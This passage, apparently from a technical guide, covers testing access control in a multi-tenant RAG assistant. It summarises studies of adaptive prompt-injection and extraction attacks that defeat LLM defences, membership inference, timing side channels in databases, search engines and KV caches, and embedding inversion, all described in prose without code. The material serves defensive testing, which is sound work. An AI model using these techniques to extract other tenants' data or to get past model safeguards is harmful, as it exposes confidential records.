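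The table also shows that tests 1 and 2 missed the removal of the tenant condition because the last check filtered the contexts before either test was applied to them. To make those two tests fail, the tester has to remove both the tenant condition and the last check at once.

Xu and Tao (2026), in *Discriminating Fixture Coverage in Agent-Infrastructure Verification Suites*, found the same kind of masking in software that displays conversations with AI agents. Their eleven checks passed a correct version and rejected a version with every fault built in, which is the usual evidence that a set of tests works. But when they removed only the code that ignores duplicate messages, all eleven checks still passed, because a second mechanism that rejected out-of-sequence messages happened to stop the duplicates too.

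Xu and Tao added a twelfth check for this, froze the set, and asked someone who had not designed the test inputs to specify ten new faults. The checks caught five. Of the other five, three made no difference on any of the test inputs, and two damaged internal data that no check examined. The first three need inputs on which the fault makes a difference, and the other two need inputs that carry the damage through to something a check examines. After they added such inputs, the checks caught all ten. Xu and Tao point out that this result covers the same ten faults and does not predict how the checks would do on new ones.

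Removing a mechanism and rerunning the tests shows whether any of them depend on it, while a count of passing tests shows little about which checks they cover. *Keep the Process, Change the Supplier* (2026) reports such removals for its software, which controls what AI agents do with tools. All 43 tests passed on the intact program. Removing the supplier eligibility check made 15 fail, and removing any one of four other mechanisms made two to four fail. At least two tests therefore depend on each of these five mechanisms, but five removals are too few to show that the whole set of tests is adequate.

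Many checks in real software have no such test. *Four Ways to Forge a Bundle My Own Verifier Calls Clean* (Hill, 2026) examines Hill's own program, which checks files of evidence about AI agents and rejects false ones. The program had 112 statements that could reject a file, and Hill could delete 75 of them, one at a time, without any test failing. Hill then fixed four known faults and wrote tests for them, but the tests still protected only 37 of the original 112 statements. The program later grew to 119 such statements, and writing a test for each unprotected one raised the number protected to 112. These are one person's measurements of one program, but they suggest that a provider who adds a test after every leak will protect the places that have already leaked and few others.

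Line coverage, the share of program lines that run during the tests, would not have revealed the problem, because the line containing Ana's tenant condition runs on every search, even if no test would fail without it. In *Mutation-Guided LLM-based Test Generation at Meta*, Foster, Harper and colleagues (2025) had a language model insert typical privacy faults into code from Meta's apps and then write tests to catch them. Of the 571 new tests, 277 added no line coverage, yet each of those caught a fault that the existing tests had missed. Engineers accepted 73% of the tests they reviewed but judged only 36% relevant to privacy, so a team that wants tests of one access rule would still have to choose among them.

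### Passes that mean nothing

Hill uses the term "vacuous pass" for a check that reports success without examining anything. In one case, an outside engineer replaced the data behind a false total with `null`. Hill's program recalculated the totals from nothing, found no mismatch and accepted the file. Hill's own measuring tools had the same problem seven times during the study. Four of those tools were meant to detect this fault, and one tool reported a perfect score. Tests of access rules can pass vacuously in at least three ways.

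The canaries may never have entered the index. Intake might skip scanned pages, drop a test document as a near-duplicate, mask the canary because it looks like an account number, or split it between two chunks. The tester can check for this by asking the same questions as a user who is allowed to read the documents. In the example, Ben receives only 34 of the 40 canaries through the stub. Four were in scanned files that intake could not read, and two had been split. Until the tester repairs these six, Ana's result cannot be used to judge whether the rules protect them.

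Ana's questions may also never come near the forbidden text. Ben's success does not rule this out, because his search covers only Birch's files, where a passage faces less competition. Kim, Pasini and Tonella (2026), in *Testing Retrieval-Augmented Generation Systems with Chunk Coverage*, define a measure that helps, the share of all chunks that a set of questions retrieves at least once. On five collections of medical and financial documents, with three chunks retrieved per question, even the full set of available questions reached only 13% to 38% of the chunks. For an access test, the share should be calculated over the forbidden chunks, with the filters turned off:

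coverage = (forbidden chunks retrieved at least once) / (all forbidden chunks in the test).

With both the tenant condition and the last check disabled, Ana's 120 questions retrieve 27 of the 40 canaries, a coverage of 67.5%. Alder documents on the same subject outrank the other 13. The tester rewrites the questions for those 13 until all 40 canaries appear, then turns the checks back on and repeats the tests. Kim and colleagues automate the question writing by giving a language model each chunk that no question has retrieved and having it write a question for that chunk. In one benchmark, Arceo and Narsing instead made forbidden text more likely to be retrieved by giving different tenants' documents embeddings with a similarity of about 0.95. Search without the filter leaked on 52% of queries.

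The third cause is a test account with unusual rights. Developers often test with an administrator's account, which can read every document, so test 1 cannot fail. An account with no rights at all receives nothing and passes every test for leaks. An account created by a script may lack the groups that real staff belong to, or may skip the company's login service. Ana's test account should therefore have the same rights as a real Alder employee and log in the same way. Before each run, the tester can confirm that the account can open one document it is allowed to read, and that the store contains at least one document it is not allowed to read.

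### Which failures should block a release

Developers usually run tests automatically whenever the code changes, and some failures block the release of the new version. A test that fails at random is a poor choice for blocking releases, because people learn to ignore it. RAGAL's evaluation had 21 questions with 27 assertions about the results, which Mușetoiu divided into two groups. Deterministic assertions check what ordinary code does, such as which kinds of document the search returned and whether the program intercepted a request for live data. If one fails, the release is blocked. Generative assertions check the model's text, such as whether it admitted not knowing something. The team reports these failures but does not block the release, because they can appear and disappear without any change to the system.

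Using a second model to judge the answers adds uncertainty. *RAG-TESTER* (2026) ran 72,000 tests on 24 combinations of language and embedding models, and a language model reported 21,633 failures. Its precision was 80.6%, so about one in five reported failures was not real. That is accurate enough to show developers where to look, but if a release required zero reported failures, false reports might block it indefinitely.

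RAGAL has one test of generated text that can block a release, which the team added after a leak. The team had masked personal details in the support tickets before indexing them. The second round of masking made 64,701 replacements, and a check found none of the targeted patterns left. Then, during a session in which people tried to make the system fail, the assistant gave a technician's full name in answer to an ordinary test question. The name was in a playbook, a set of repair instructions based on past tickets. The masking program had a list of usernames but did not recognise full names in email headers and signatures, and the check looked only for patterns the program already knew.

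The team built a list of 523 full names and masked them. For every question, the evaluation now also checks that the answer contains no name on the list, with first and last names in either order. The model's wording still varies, so this test can miss a leak on a given run, but if a name appears, it must have come from text that should have been masked. Likewise, finding a canary in a real model's answer should block the release, although finding none proves little.

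Alder and Birch's provider could run tests 1, 2 and 5 and the exact comparison of contexts in test 4 before every release, and block the release if any of them fails. The removals in test 7 and the timed trials in test 6 take longer and could run overnight. A person would review differences in the real model's wording.

RAGAL's leak test still has the weakness that caused the incident, because it uses the same list as the masking program. If a name is missing from the list, the program won't mask it and the test won't find it. A canary avoids this problem because the tester chooses the string and the system has no list of canaries.

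## Attack the system and read the results correctly

Scripted tests catch faults that someone thought to look for. In an attack campaign, people or programs try to break a rule by any means within agreed limits, and they change their approach after each failure. For Ana's rule, the main purpose of a campaign is to find what the inventory of paths missed, such as a forgotten export page or a request field that nobody checks. A campaign also measures how well rules that still depend on the model hold up, which tests of the code can't do.

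### Design the campaign

A result such as "no leaks" means little without a record of what the attackers could do. For the assistant that Alder and Birch share, the provider might choose these settings:

| Choice | Setting | What a weaker setting could miss |
|---|---|---|
| Accounts | Two ordinary Alder accounts, and one that has just lost access to a Birch contract | Leaks that need two users or a withdrawn permission |
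| Write access | Attackers may upload files to Alder's folder and email its staff | Instructions hidden in documents |
| Knowledge | The code, the system prompt and a description of every filter | Attacks aimed at a particular defence |
| Attempts | 5,000 requests over two weeks, with every reply visible to the attackers | Attacks that improve through feedback |
| Success | Any canary or listed fact from Birch's files reaches an attacker, in any wording or code | Paraphrased or disguised leaks |

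Attackers can succeed much more often when they know how a system is defended. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tested a defence called MELON, which runs the model twice and compares the actions it tries to take. An automated attack succeeded 76% of the time without information about MELON, and 95% of the time with its published description and code. The paper recommends telling human attackers about every defence in the system.

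The number of attempts matters just as much. The main experiments in *LeakDojo* (Zhang, Dong and colleagues, 2026) gave each attack 200 questions. One attack that was allowed to continue had covered 30.4% of a document collection after 500 questions, 47.0% after 1,000 and 83.7% after 6,000.

Researchers often count a leak only when an answer copies much of a document. Zhang and colleagues require the answer to reproduce more than half of a retrieved passage. By that standard, an answer that revealed only Birch's pallet rate would probably count as safe. A person should also check doubtful cases. Nasr and colleagues verified every successful attack by hand because models that judge answers can be fooled.

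For part of the testing, the attackers should replace the model with their own program, so that each of these attempts tests the code around the model. After each successful attack, the provider fixes the fault, adds a scripted test for it, and lets the attackers try again with full knowledge of the fix.

### Models that apply access rules themselves

A model left to enforce a rule can fail to do so even without an attack. Klisura, Khoury and colleagues (2025), in *Role-Conditioned Refusals*, tested this with about 55,000 ordinary questions about 233 databases, taken from two public collections, Spider and BIRD. They gave each database four roles, ranging from one with full access to one limited to a few harmless tables. The model received a question, the layout of the database and the role's permissions, and had to write a database query if the role allowed it or refuse otherwise. A separate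 program worked out the correct decision from the permissions.

The researchers compared three designs. With prompting, one model decided whether to allow the request and wrote the query. With verification, one model wrote the query and a second model call checked it against the permissions. The prompts for these two designs contained no worked examples. With fine-tuning, the researchers trained two small models further on examples of permitted and forbidden requests from Spider. The table gives F1 scores for refusals, where 1 is perfect.

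| Model | Spider: prompting | Spider: verification | Spider: fine-tuning | BIRD: prompting | BIRD: verification | BIRD: fine-tuning |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 0.797 | 0.877 | – | 0.701 | 0.852 | – |
| DeepSeek-R1 (14B) | 0.832 | 0.883 | – | 0.757 | 0.851 | – |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 0.713 | 0.871 | 0.878 | 0.633 | 0.839 | 0.646 |
| Mistral 7B | 0.599 | 0.874 | 0.933 | 0.552 | 0.816 | 0.663 |

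Verification helped every model here, except that it lowered GPT-4o-mini's score on Spider from 0.832 to 0.775 when the prompt included a few worked examples. Fine-tuning gave the best score on Spider but did much worse on BIRD, whose databases were not in the training data.

Longer permissions caused more mistakes. Klisura and colleagues report these rates of wrongly allowed requests on BIRD:

| Average length of the permissions | Prompting (GPT) | Verification (GPT) | Fine-tuning (Mistral) |
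|---|---|---|---|
| 2,700 characters | 12.8% | 5.5% | 8.0% |
| 8,000 characters | 22.8% | 17.3% | 20.0% |
| 22,700 characters | 19.2% | 33.0% | 40.0% |

The 33.0% conflicts with their finding that the verifier refused 97.4% of forbidden requests under the longest permissions, which would mean it wrongly allowed only 2.6%. Either rate would be far too high for Ana's rule.

Smaller models sometimes began a response with "Access Denied" and then wrote the forbidden query anyway. A test that only searched for the refusal phrase would have counted these failures as refusals.

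These models are small by current standards, and newer ones would probably score higher. But the program that supplied the correct answers applied the rule exactly in every case, using the same permissions the models received. When a rule is this precise, a developer can use such a program as the access check and doesn't need a model.

### Defences that passed fixed attacks

Many developers test a defence with a published list of attacks. Nasr and colleagues examined 12 defences against prompt injection and jailbreaks (attempts to make a model ignore its safety training). For most of them, the reported attack success rate was near zero. The team then ran adaptive attacks against each one. An automated adaptive attack tries several wordings, scores the system's reply to each, and uses the most promising wordings to produce the next round.

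Two of the defences changed the prompt, one by marking the trusted text with special symbols and the other by repeating the user's request after the untrusted text. Fixed attacks succeeded against them as little as 1% of the time, and adaptive attacks more than 95% of the time. Against a model trained to resist injection, fixed attacks succeeded 2% of the time and adaptive attacks 96%. Adaptive attacks also got past three separate detection models more than 90% of the time and a fourth 71% of the time.

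More than 500 people took part in a related competition. The automated search succeeded in 69% of a selected set of scenarios, while the human attackers together succeeded in all of them.

The researchers gave the attacks plenty of computing power, and the attacks on detectors had access to the detector's confidence score. They tested whether each defence could be broken and did not study how hard it was to break. Their success rates therefore don't predict how often real attackers would succeed, but they show that the original near-zero figures were not evidence of robustness. None of the 12 defences was a permission check in ordinary code.

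The same thing happens when the rule is an instruction not to reveal stored documents. In *External Data Extraction Attacks against Retrieval-Augmented Large Language Models*, He, Chen and colleagues (2025) built RAG systems on 1,000 entries from a medical dataset and tried to extract them with about 300 questions. They compared their own adaptive attack, which uses a language model to improve its wording, with five others.

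| Model | Other attacks, with the instruction | Adaptive attack, no instruction | Adaptive attack, with the instruction |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 0% | 36.5% | 34.0% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 0–16.4% | 49.1% | 48.1% |
| GPT-4o mini | 0% | 48.3% | 45.7% |
| DeepSeek-V3 | 0–17.8% | 48.7% | 49.4% |

The figures are shares of the documents extracted almost word for word. On GPT-4o mini, the instruction lowered extraction by the adaptive attack by less than three percentage points. A developer who tested only the five other attacks would have concluded that the instruction worked perfectly. The adaptive attack needed fewer than 16 trial requests on average to find effective wording against Gemini.

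### How other parts of the pipeline affect leakage

Zhang and colleagues built LeakDojo to find out which parts of a RAG system make extraction easier. They ran six known attacks against 14 models and four document collections. In these tests the attacker may retrieve any document, and a leak means that the model copies a retrieved passage into its answer. They found that

leakage ≈ trigger rate × coverage.

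The trigger rate is the share of questions that make the model copy a passage. Coverage is the number of different passages the questions retrieve, divided by the most they could have retrieved. Leakage uses the same denominator.

For example, one attack on a collection of Enron emails had a trigger rate of 100% and coverage of 88.4% with Gemini 3 Flash. The formula predicts 88.4% leakage, and the researchers measured 88.3%. With DeepSeek-V3, the same attack had a trigger rate of 12.0% and leakage was 6.8%. But a different attack extracted 64.4% from DeepSeek-V3, so a tester who tried only the first attack could have judged the model fairly safe.

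A working access filter reduces Ana's coverage of Birch's files to zero, so coverage multiplied by trigger rate is also zero, however high the trigger rate is.

Zhang and colleagues then added components to a basic pipeline one at a time. These are the results for one model, Gemma 3 27B, on financial documents. Faithfulness measures how closely normal answers follow the retrieved text.

| Pipeline | Leakage | Faithfulness |
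|---|---|---|
| Search only | 48.0% | 91.9% |
| With a reranker | 45.2% | 89.6% |
| With a reranker and a rewriter | 39.2% | 89.6% |
| With a reranker, a rewriter and a summariser | 8.5% | 78.5% |

A reranker made little difference across the models tested. A rewriter, which turns the user's question into several searches, can help an attacker because even a badly chosen question then finds more documents. With a rewriter, coverage rose from 52% to about 69% on medical documents and from 84% to about 89% on financial ones, but fell from 83% to about 79% on scientific ones. More coverage did not always lead to more leakage, as the table shows.

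The summariser, which passes on only the parts of each passage that seem relevant, usually reduced leakage a great deal, but on medical documents, for example, leakage from Kimi K2 rose from 4.0% to 7.0%. The reduction is also weak evidence that short facts are protected, because the researchers instructed their summariser to keep relevant numbers exactly as written. It would keep Birch's pallet rate while removing most of the contract around it.

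In one test, a model that screened incoming questions reduced the leakage caused by the six attacks to between 0.2% and 2.0%. When the researchers disguised the request for documents as a harmless task, leakage rose to between 11.3% and 59.6%, depending on how the attack chose its questions. Adding a filter that blocked close copies in the output reduced leakage to between 3.2% and 30.0%.

### Injection rates for 2026 models

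Recent models resist prompt injection much better than those in the 2025 studies. Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) quotes results that Anthropic published in July for a benchmark of instructions hidden in material that a model reads:

| Model | Attacker succeeds on one attempt | Attacker succeeds within 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 2.0% |
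| Claude Mythos 5 | – | 2.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 5.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | – | 5.9% |
| Muse Spark | – | 16.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | – | 20.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | – | 20.8% |

The security firm Gray Swan developed the benchmark. In September, the *System Card* for Claude Mythos 5.1 (Anthropic, 2026) called the model Anthropic's most robust so far on this benchmark. According to the technology news site The Decoder, attacks on Opus 5 in a web browser also failed in all 129 test scenarios.

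A model's attack success rate can vary widely with the setting. VentureBeat reports that Claude Opus 4.6 withstood all 200 attack attempts in a restricted coding environment. When the same model operated a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. Within 200 attempts, attackers succeeded in 78.6% of cases without extra safeguards and 57.1% with them.

The provider of Ana's assistant can't use a benchmark figure as the assistant's failure rate, because the assistant has different documents, tools and instructions. The benchmark also covers hidden instructions but not an employee who tries to trick the assistant with direct questions. A supplier's published rate can help the provider choose a model, but the provider has to run its own attacks to measure how often the assistant fails.

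### What a run with no leaks can show

Suppose each request has the same probability *p* of causing a leak, independently of the others. The chance of seeing no leaks in *n* requests is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. The 95% upper bound is the value of *p* at which this chance falls to 5%:

*p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/*n*) ≈ 3/*n*.

Arceo and Narsing's access gate had no leaks in 300 cross-tenant probes and none in 90 injection probes. For random probes, these results are compatible with true leak rates of up to about 1% and 3.3%, respectively. For the 129 browser scenarios that Opus 5 passed, the corresponding upper bound is about 2.3%.

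Even a much lower rate adds up with use. The chance of at least one failure in *k* independent attempts is

1 − (1 − *p*)ᵏ.

If a security rule fails in 0.1% of attempts, the chance of at least one failure in 1,000 independent attempts is 1 − 0.999¹⁰⁰⁰, or about 63%. Fifty employees who each asked 20 questions would reach 1,000 attempts in a single day.

Repeated attacks are often not independent. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports tests in which a single strong attack succeeded 4.7% of the time, while the chance of at least one success was 33.6% in ten attempts and 63% in 100. If the attempts had been independent, those last two rates would have been 38% and over 99%. They were probably lower because some scenarios were easy to attack and others were so hard that repeated attempts kept failing. An attacker who learns from each failure could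 do better than independent attempts would. Testers should therefore measure the success rate at several numbers of attempts instead of calculating it from the rate for one.

Probes are also not independent if they are too alike. Three hundred versions of one question may all test the same few lines of code and provide little more evidence than one question.

The larger problem is that an attacker looks for the request most likely to cause a leak, while random probes estimate the average probability of a leak across the requests in the test. That average can be below 1% even if one request causes a leak every time.

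Suppose the search code leaves out the tenant condition whenever a question contains a particular punctuation mark, which appears in one question in 10,000. Three hundred random questions would miss the fault 97% of the time, but someone who noticed it could retrieve Birch's files every time by including the mark in each request. More random probes would lower the bound on the average failure rate but still set no limit on what this attacker could do.

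A campaign by skilled attackers more directly tests the requests that matter, but it doesn't produce a bound either, for the reason Anderson gave about tiger teams. The provider should report what was done, for instance "three people with the source code made 5,000 requests and obtained nothing from Birch", and not convert this into a failure rate of 0.06%.

### Where a rule in the prompt still helps

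Lower failure rates are useful because many attackers get only a few chances. If a supplier's PDF contains one hidden instruction that Ana's assistant reads once, using a model that obeys such instructions 0.2% of the time removes most of the risk. Prompted rules also stop attackers who don't adapt. In He and colleagues' experiment, one of the other attacks extracted 39.2% of the documents from GPT-4o mini without the instruction and none with it. Anthropic also found that safety instructions in the system prompt of its chat service improved how Mythos 5.1 handled harmful requests.

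A prompted rule can also catch some errors that the access filter can't. If intake has mislabelled a Birch contract, the instruction "Never reveal anything from Birch's files" might still stop the model from quoting it, because Birch's name is at the top.

Other rules can't be stated exactly enough to code. An assistant for a personnel department might have to reveal only as much of an employee's medical history as a manager's question requires. A permission table can keep the file from people with no right to read it, but it can't decide how much detail a permitted manager needs, so the provider has to leave that judgement to a model or a person. The provider can agree on an acceptable failure rate with its clients and measure the actual rate with an adaptive attack campaign each time the model changes.

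The extra verifier layer can block requests that users are entitled to make. In Klisura and colleagues' tests, only 53% of the verifier's refusals were correct under the longest permissions. Zhang and colleagues found that models that scored higher on following instructions tended to leak more (a correlation of 0.58), perhaps because an attacker's request to copy the context is also an instruction.

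A provider also can't simply multiply the failure rates of its layers. If a detector misses 2% of attacks and the model follows 2% of hidden instructions, the combined rate is 0.04% only if the two fail independently. An attacker can search for wording that gets past both, and Nasr and colleagues' adaptive attacks still succeeded against a system that combined several detectors.

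## Look for leaks that remain when the access check works

In an attack campaign, testers usually count an attack as successful when some of Birch's text reaches the attacker. But a search that returns only Alder's passages can still leak information about Birch's files. It can take slightly longer when Birch has a matching file, or give one of Alder's passages a lower score because Birch's files use the same word. Security engineers call such an unintended signal a side channel. Side channels break noninterference, the requirement that files Ana may not read change nothing she can observe. The shortened list from the post-filtered search, with two sources instead of five, is also a side channel, but it is easier to notice than the other two.

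### Why a hidden row takes time

*Plaintext Recovery Against Post-Filtering Access Control* (Espiritu and Cash, 2026) studies PostgreSQL, whose row-level security adds an access rule to every query. The database can apply this rule before or after the user's own search condition. If the search condition runs first, it can expose hidden data through an error. For example, a condition that divides by a stored value fails if a hidden row contains zero, and the error message reveals the zero. PostgreSQL therefore normally applies the access rule first, but this often stops it from using an index on the searched column, so it has to read the whole table.

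To avoid that cost, PostgreSQL treats some operators, including "equals" and "less than", as `LEAKPROOF`, meaning that they have no visible side effects such as errors. If a condition uses only these operators, the database may look up the matching rows in an index and apply the access rule to them afterwards. For a condition *Q*, a table *T* and an access rule *P*, the query then takes about

time(*Q*, *T*) + time(*P*, *Q*(*T*)),

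where *Q*(*T*) is the set of matching rows before the rule removes any. If no row matches, the database has nothing to check. If a hidden row matches, the database checks it and removes it. The user gets an empty result in both cases, but the second takes longer.

### From an existence test to whole records

Earlier researchers had used this delay to test whether a chosen value existed. Finding a nine-digit identity number this way is slow because there are a billion candidates. Espiritu and Cash tested ranges instead. Each test shows whether a range contains any hidden numbers, and the next test halves the range, so about 30 correct results identify one number. Conditions on several columns then show which values belong to the same row.

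The researchers built a hospital database with one million patients and 10,000 clinics, in which doctors could read only their own clinic's records. The attacker had a doctor's account and could run any read query. The attack's accuracy depended on how the access rule found the doctor's clinic, how busy the server was, and how often the attacker repeated each query. Random guessing would be right 50% of the time.

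| How the rule finds the clinic | Processor load | One measurement | Four | Eight |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Looks it up in a second table | No added load | 100.0% | 100.0% | 100.0% |
| Looks it up in a second table | 95% | 96.4% | 99.9% | 99.99% |
| Reads a session setting | No added load | 72.7% | 89.3% | 95.6% |
| Reads a session setting | 95% | 50.5% | 54.1% | 60.2% |

The table lookup makes each check slower, which makes the delay easier to detect. Distance helped the defender only a little. With the attacker about 3,000 km away and the server at 50% load, one measurement was right 95.5% of the time, and using eight raised this to 99.7%. Disk encryption had no effect, because the database works on decrypted data in memory.

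The attack on the slower rule recovered 99.99% of the million identity numbers in about two and a half hours, using 40 million queries. Espiritu and Cash estimate that trying every number would have taken two billion queries and almost three days. In a separate test, they gave the program the values that appeared in 100,000 rows, and it reassembled every row in 1.3 hours. It had to start with the most distinctive column, since one other order found only 46% of the rows. The conditions favoured the attacker, because the database fitted in memory and nothing limited the number of queries.

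The fix sorts the index by clinic and then by the searched value, and rewrites the access rule so that the database can use the clinic condition when it plans the search. The database then examines only the rows from the doctor's own clinic. Together, the two changes reduced the attack's accuracy to between 49.0% and 52.5%, which is no better than guessing, but either change alone left it at 100%. The fix suits simple rules such as "same clinic" or "same tenant", but not rules that need complex logic for each row. It also slows searches by staff who may read every clinic's records, and a table with many searchable columns needs many such indexes.

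### Scores that depend on hidden documents

Elasticsearch and OpenSearch are text search engines that can restrict which documents each user sees. They rank results with a formula called BM25, which gives rare words more weight. If *n* of the *N* documents in an index contain a word, its weight is

log(1 + (*N* − *n* + 0.5) / (*n* + 0.5)).

Both engines count hidden documents in *N* and *n*. Suppose Alder and Birch have 800 documents in one index, and a single Alder document mentions a company that Birch secretly plans to buy. The company's name has a weight of 6.28 if no Birch document contains it and 5.77 if one does, which lowers the Alder document's score by about 8%. This kind of dependence is why the contexts changed order when the tester deleted Birch's files.

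According to Elastic's *Security limitations*, a restricted user can learn words that appear only in inaccessible documents and count the documents that contain them. Earlier attacks had to guess the whole word. Espiritu and Cash could discover an unknown word letter by letter by using autocomplete queries, whose scores also depend on whether any hidden word begins with the queried letters. Some indexes also store runs of up to four words to show results while the user types. The attack recovered short phrases from these runs and joined the overlapping ones into approximate text.

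The attack recovered every stored run of one to four words from 1,000 Enron emails, with no false ones, in six hours and about 32 million queries. With ten emails, it took four minutes. The attacker had to see the scores and be able to add documents to the index. Espiritu and Cash call this a best case for the attacker, partly because nobody else changed the index during the attack.

One remedy is to calculate word counts only from documents the user may read. Another is to take the counts from an unrelated public collection, but this does not fix autocomplete, where the score still changes if a hidden word matches. There, the engine should consider only words in visible documents or leave the autocomplete part out of the score. Espiritu and Cash reported their findings to the developers in January 2026. Elastic said the problem was a low priority, and PostgreSQL and OpenSearch acknowledged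 the reports.

### What carries over to an assistant that only takes questions

These attacks are strongest when the attacker can write database queries. Espiritu and Cash leave open whether the attacks can recover records through an application that offers only fixed types of query. Ana types a sentence, which the pipeline turns into an embedding, so she can't query the database for a range of numbers. The model also takes seconds to answer, and that time varies enough to hide a very small delay in the search unless she repeats the question many times. Recovering whole records this way is probably hard, but nobody has shown that it is impossible.

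Some common features make it easier:

- **Search tools with filters:** If the model fills in dates or amounts, the hostile-model assumption gives the attacker control of those fields, and range queries become possible again.
- **A separate search box:** It may offer autocomplete or display relevance scores.
- **Uploads to a shared keyword index:** Ana can add a document and watch how it ranks. Hiding the score doesn't help if its position in the list changes.
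- **Answers that appear word by word:** The time to the first word leaves out most of the model's writing time, so it is a cleaner signal.

The server that runs the model can also leak information through timing. It often caches intermediate results for text it has recently processed. If tenants share this cache, the model starts responding sooner to a prompt that repeats another tenant's text. Sun, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Agent-Assisted Side-Channel Attacks on Non-Prefix KV Cache in RAG*, measured a difference of 17.68 milliseconds for a 300-token prompt that matched from the first token, but only 0.06 milliseconds, too small to detect, when the beginning didn't match. An ordinary cache is therefore hard to exploit if private text, such as a user's conversation history, comes before the documents.

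Newer caches can reuse the results computed for a document wherever it appears in the prompt. Sun and colleagues used one of these caches to recover private text from other users' prompts in tests where the possible wording was limited. Padding the text to fixed lengths and equalising the processing time removed the signal that revealed the text and reduced throughput only slightly. Caches that accept similar rather than identical text also produce measurable delays, according to *Selective KV-Cache Sharing to Mitigate Timing Side-Channels in LLM Inference* (2025).

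### Is this document in the store?

Membership inference is an attempt to find out whether a particular document is in the store. The answer can be sensitive even if the attacker already has the text. For example, someone with a copy of a draft merger agreement might want to know whether Birch has it on file.

Liu, Zhang and Long (2025), in *Mask-based Membership Inference Attacks for Retrieval-Augmented Generation*, removed words from a document and asked the system to fill them in. The system filled in about 90% of the words correctly when the document was in the store and 20% when it wasn't. Nguyen, Ma and colleagues (2026), in *Five Queries Are Enough*, asked five ordinary-looking questions per document and checked whether the document supported the claims in the answers. Their AUC, the probability that a stored document scores higher than an absent one, reached 0.991, where 0.5 is chance.

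Other retrieved documents can obscure the signal by answering the same question. In *DCMI*, Gao, Meng and colleagues (2025) reduced this interference by comparing responses before and after a small change to the question. Their attack reached an AUC of 0.974 when they could see the model's output probabilities and had a sample of the store. On MaxKB, a real RAG platform, it succeeded at most 74% of the time.

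None of these three studies assumes a per-user access filter. With a pre-filter, Birch's document can't enter Ana's context, so her answers can't depend on it. The results don't show a weakness in a working filter, but a tester can use the same method to check whether a filter works. Ana asks about 50 documents from Birch's files and 50 similar documents that neither firm has. If the tester can use her answers to tell the two groups apart better than chance, Birch's files are influencing those answers.

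### What stored vectors reveal

Ana never sees embeddings, but a database provider or someone who steals a backup might. Morris, Kuleshov and colleagues (2023) showed in *Text Embeddings Reveal (Almost) As Much As Text* that such a person could often reconstruct the text. Their program, Vec2Text, guesses the text, then repeatedly embeds the guess, compares the result with the stolen embedding and corrects the guess. It recovered 92% of 32-token passages exactly, and 89% of the full names in short extracts from clinical notes. Longer passages were harder to recover exactly. For one OpenAI embedding model, the rate fell from 60.9% for passages with about 32 tokens to 8.0% for passages averaging 81 tokens.

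*How Much Do Modern Embeddings Reveal?* (Elaasar and Lopes, 2026) tested the method on newer commercial models, with at most five rounds of correction. For OpenAI's text-embedding-3-small, the method recovered 47.4% of health-related prompts and 24.5% of general ones exactly, ignoring capitalization and spacing. Stock phrases may have made the health prompts easier to recover. Most RAG chunks are longer than the 60 to 80 characters tested, so exact recovery would be rarer. But an attacker who wants Birch's pallet rate needs only one number, and the paper did not measure how often numbers were recovered correctly.

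According to a review of inversion methods in *Embedding Inference Attack* (Raelijohn, Gambs and Rajotte, 2026), the attacker also needs either access to the embedding model or a leaked set of embeddings with their texts. Keeping the model's name secret may not help, because if the search covers public documents, an attacker can compare the search results with those of likely models and identify the one in use.

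Adding random noise to the embeddings gives less protection than early results suggested. Morris and colleagues found that a small amount cut Vec2Text's reconstruction score to 13% of its original value and reduced search quality by only 2%. Wang, Cui and colleagues (2026), in *Denoising-Aware Inversion*, later trained a program to remove the noise before reconstruction. Their method's reconstruction score was about two and a half times that of Vec2Text on the same kind of noisy embeddings.

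Another defence is geometric access control, which gives each tenant's embeddings a secret transformation. Some designs rotate the vectors, and others add coordinates that mark the tenant. Nouyep and colleagues show when such a marker guarantees separation. If it has length *M* and different tenants' markers are at right angles, two vectors with original similarity *s* have a new similarity of

(*s* + *M*²) / (1 + *M*²)

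within a tenant, and at most 1 / (1 + *M*²) between tenants. Since *s* is never below −1, every Alder chunk outranks every Birch chunk if *M*² is greater than 2. A huge *M* causes a different problem, because the differences in *s* become too small for the computer to represent. In one such test, the search found only 2% of the right results.

These secret transformations cut the share of test queries that returned at least one forbidden chunk from 100% to zero. But a program with no keys and no original embeddings could still sort the stored vectors by access policy almost perfectly, because embeddings tend to cluster around a common average and each transformation moves that average to a different place.

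If the provider helped a user obtain 200 to 400 pairs of another tenant's original and transformed embeddings, the user could undo the transformation well enough to reproduce 80% of the search results. Forging a query that the search would accept as another tenant's took 500 to 1,800 pairs if each tenant had its own secret transformation. One design used the same rotation for everyone, so users could learn it from 200 to 300 of their own pairs and needed only one pair from the target. Combining two designs did not help much. Nouyep and colleagues suggest that a trusted server authenticate each transformed query and that providers change the secrets regularly, but they have not tested either measure.

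Encryption can hide the vectors and still reveal which records a search returns. *More Than You Expect!* (Zhang, He and colleagues, 2026) tests what a server can learn from record numbers alone. Records that often appear together tend to concern the same subject, so a server that knew the categories of 1% of the records could infer the rest with 84.3% accuracy on the easiest of four datasets and 27.8% on the hardest. The provider of Ana's assistant should therefore restrict access to embeddings as strictly as to documents, and delete both together.

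### A timing test with three kinds of question

The sample specification leaves response time to a separate test. The tester can run one as follows, using Ana's account.

1. Write three sets of questions of similar length and form. The first concerns subjects on which neither firm has files. The second matches documents Ana may read, and the third matches only Birch's documents.
2. Turn off the answer cache, which would otherwise answer the repeated questions. Send the questions in random order, so that a busy period affects all three sets equally.
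3. For each measurement, send a question eight times and keep the shortest time, since most interference adds delay.
4. In a trial run, find the typical times for the first and third sets, and fix the threshold halfway between them. Fix the pass mark as well.
5. In the main run, take 1,000 new measurements for each of these two sets. Count a measurement as correct if the threshold puts it in the right set.

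If Birch's files have no effect on timing, about 50% of the 2,000 measurements will be correct. The standard error is √(0.25 / 2,000), or 1.1 percentage points, so a result above 53% would occur by chance in only about four of every 1,000 tests. The tester can use 53% as the threshold for detecting a leak.

The questions about Alder's documents check the measurement. If they appear to take as long as questions that match nothing, the timing may be too coarse to detect a leak. The tester should then time the search service directly instead of the whole answer.

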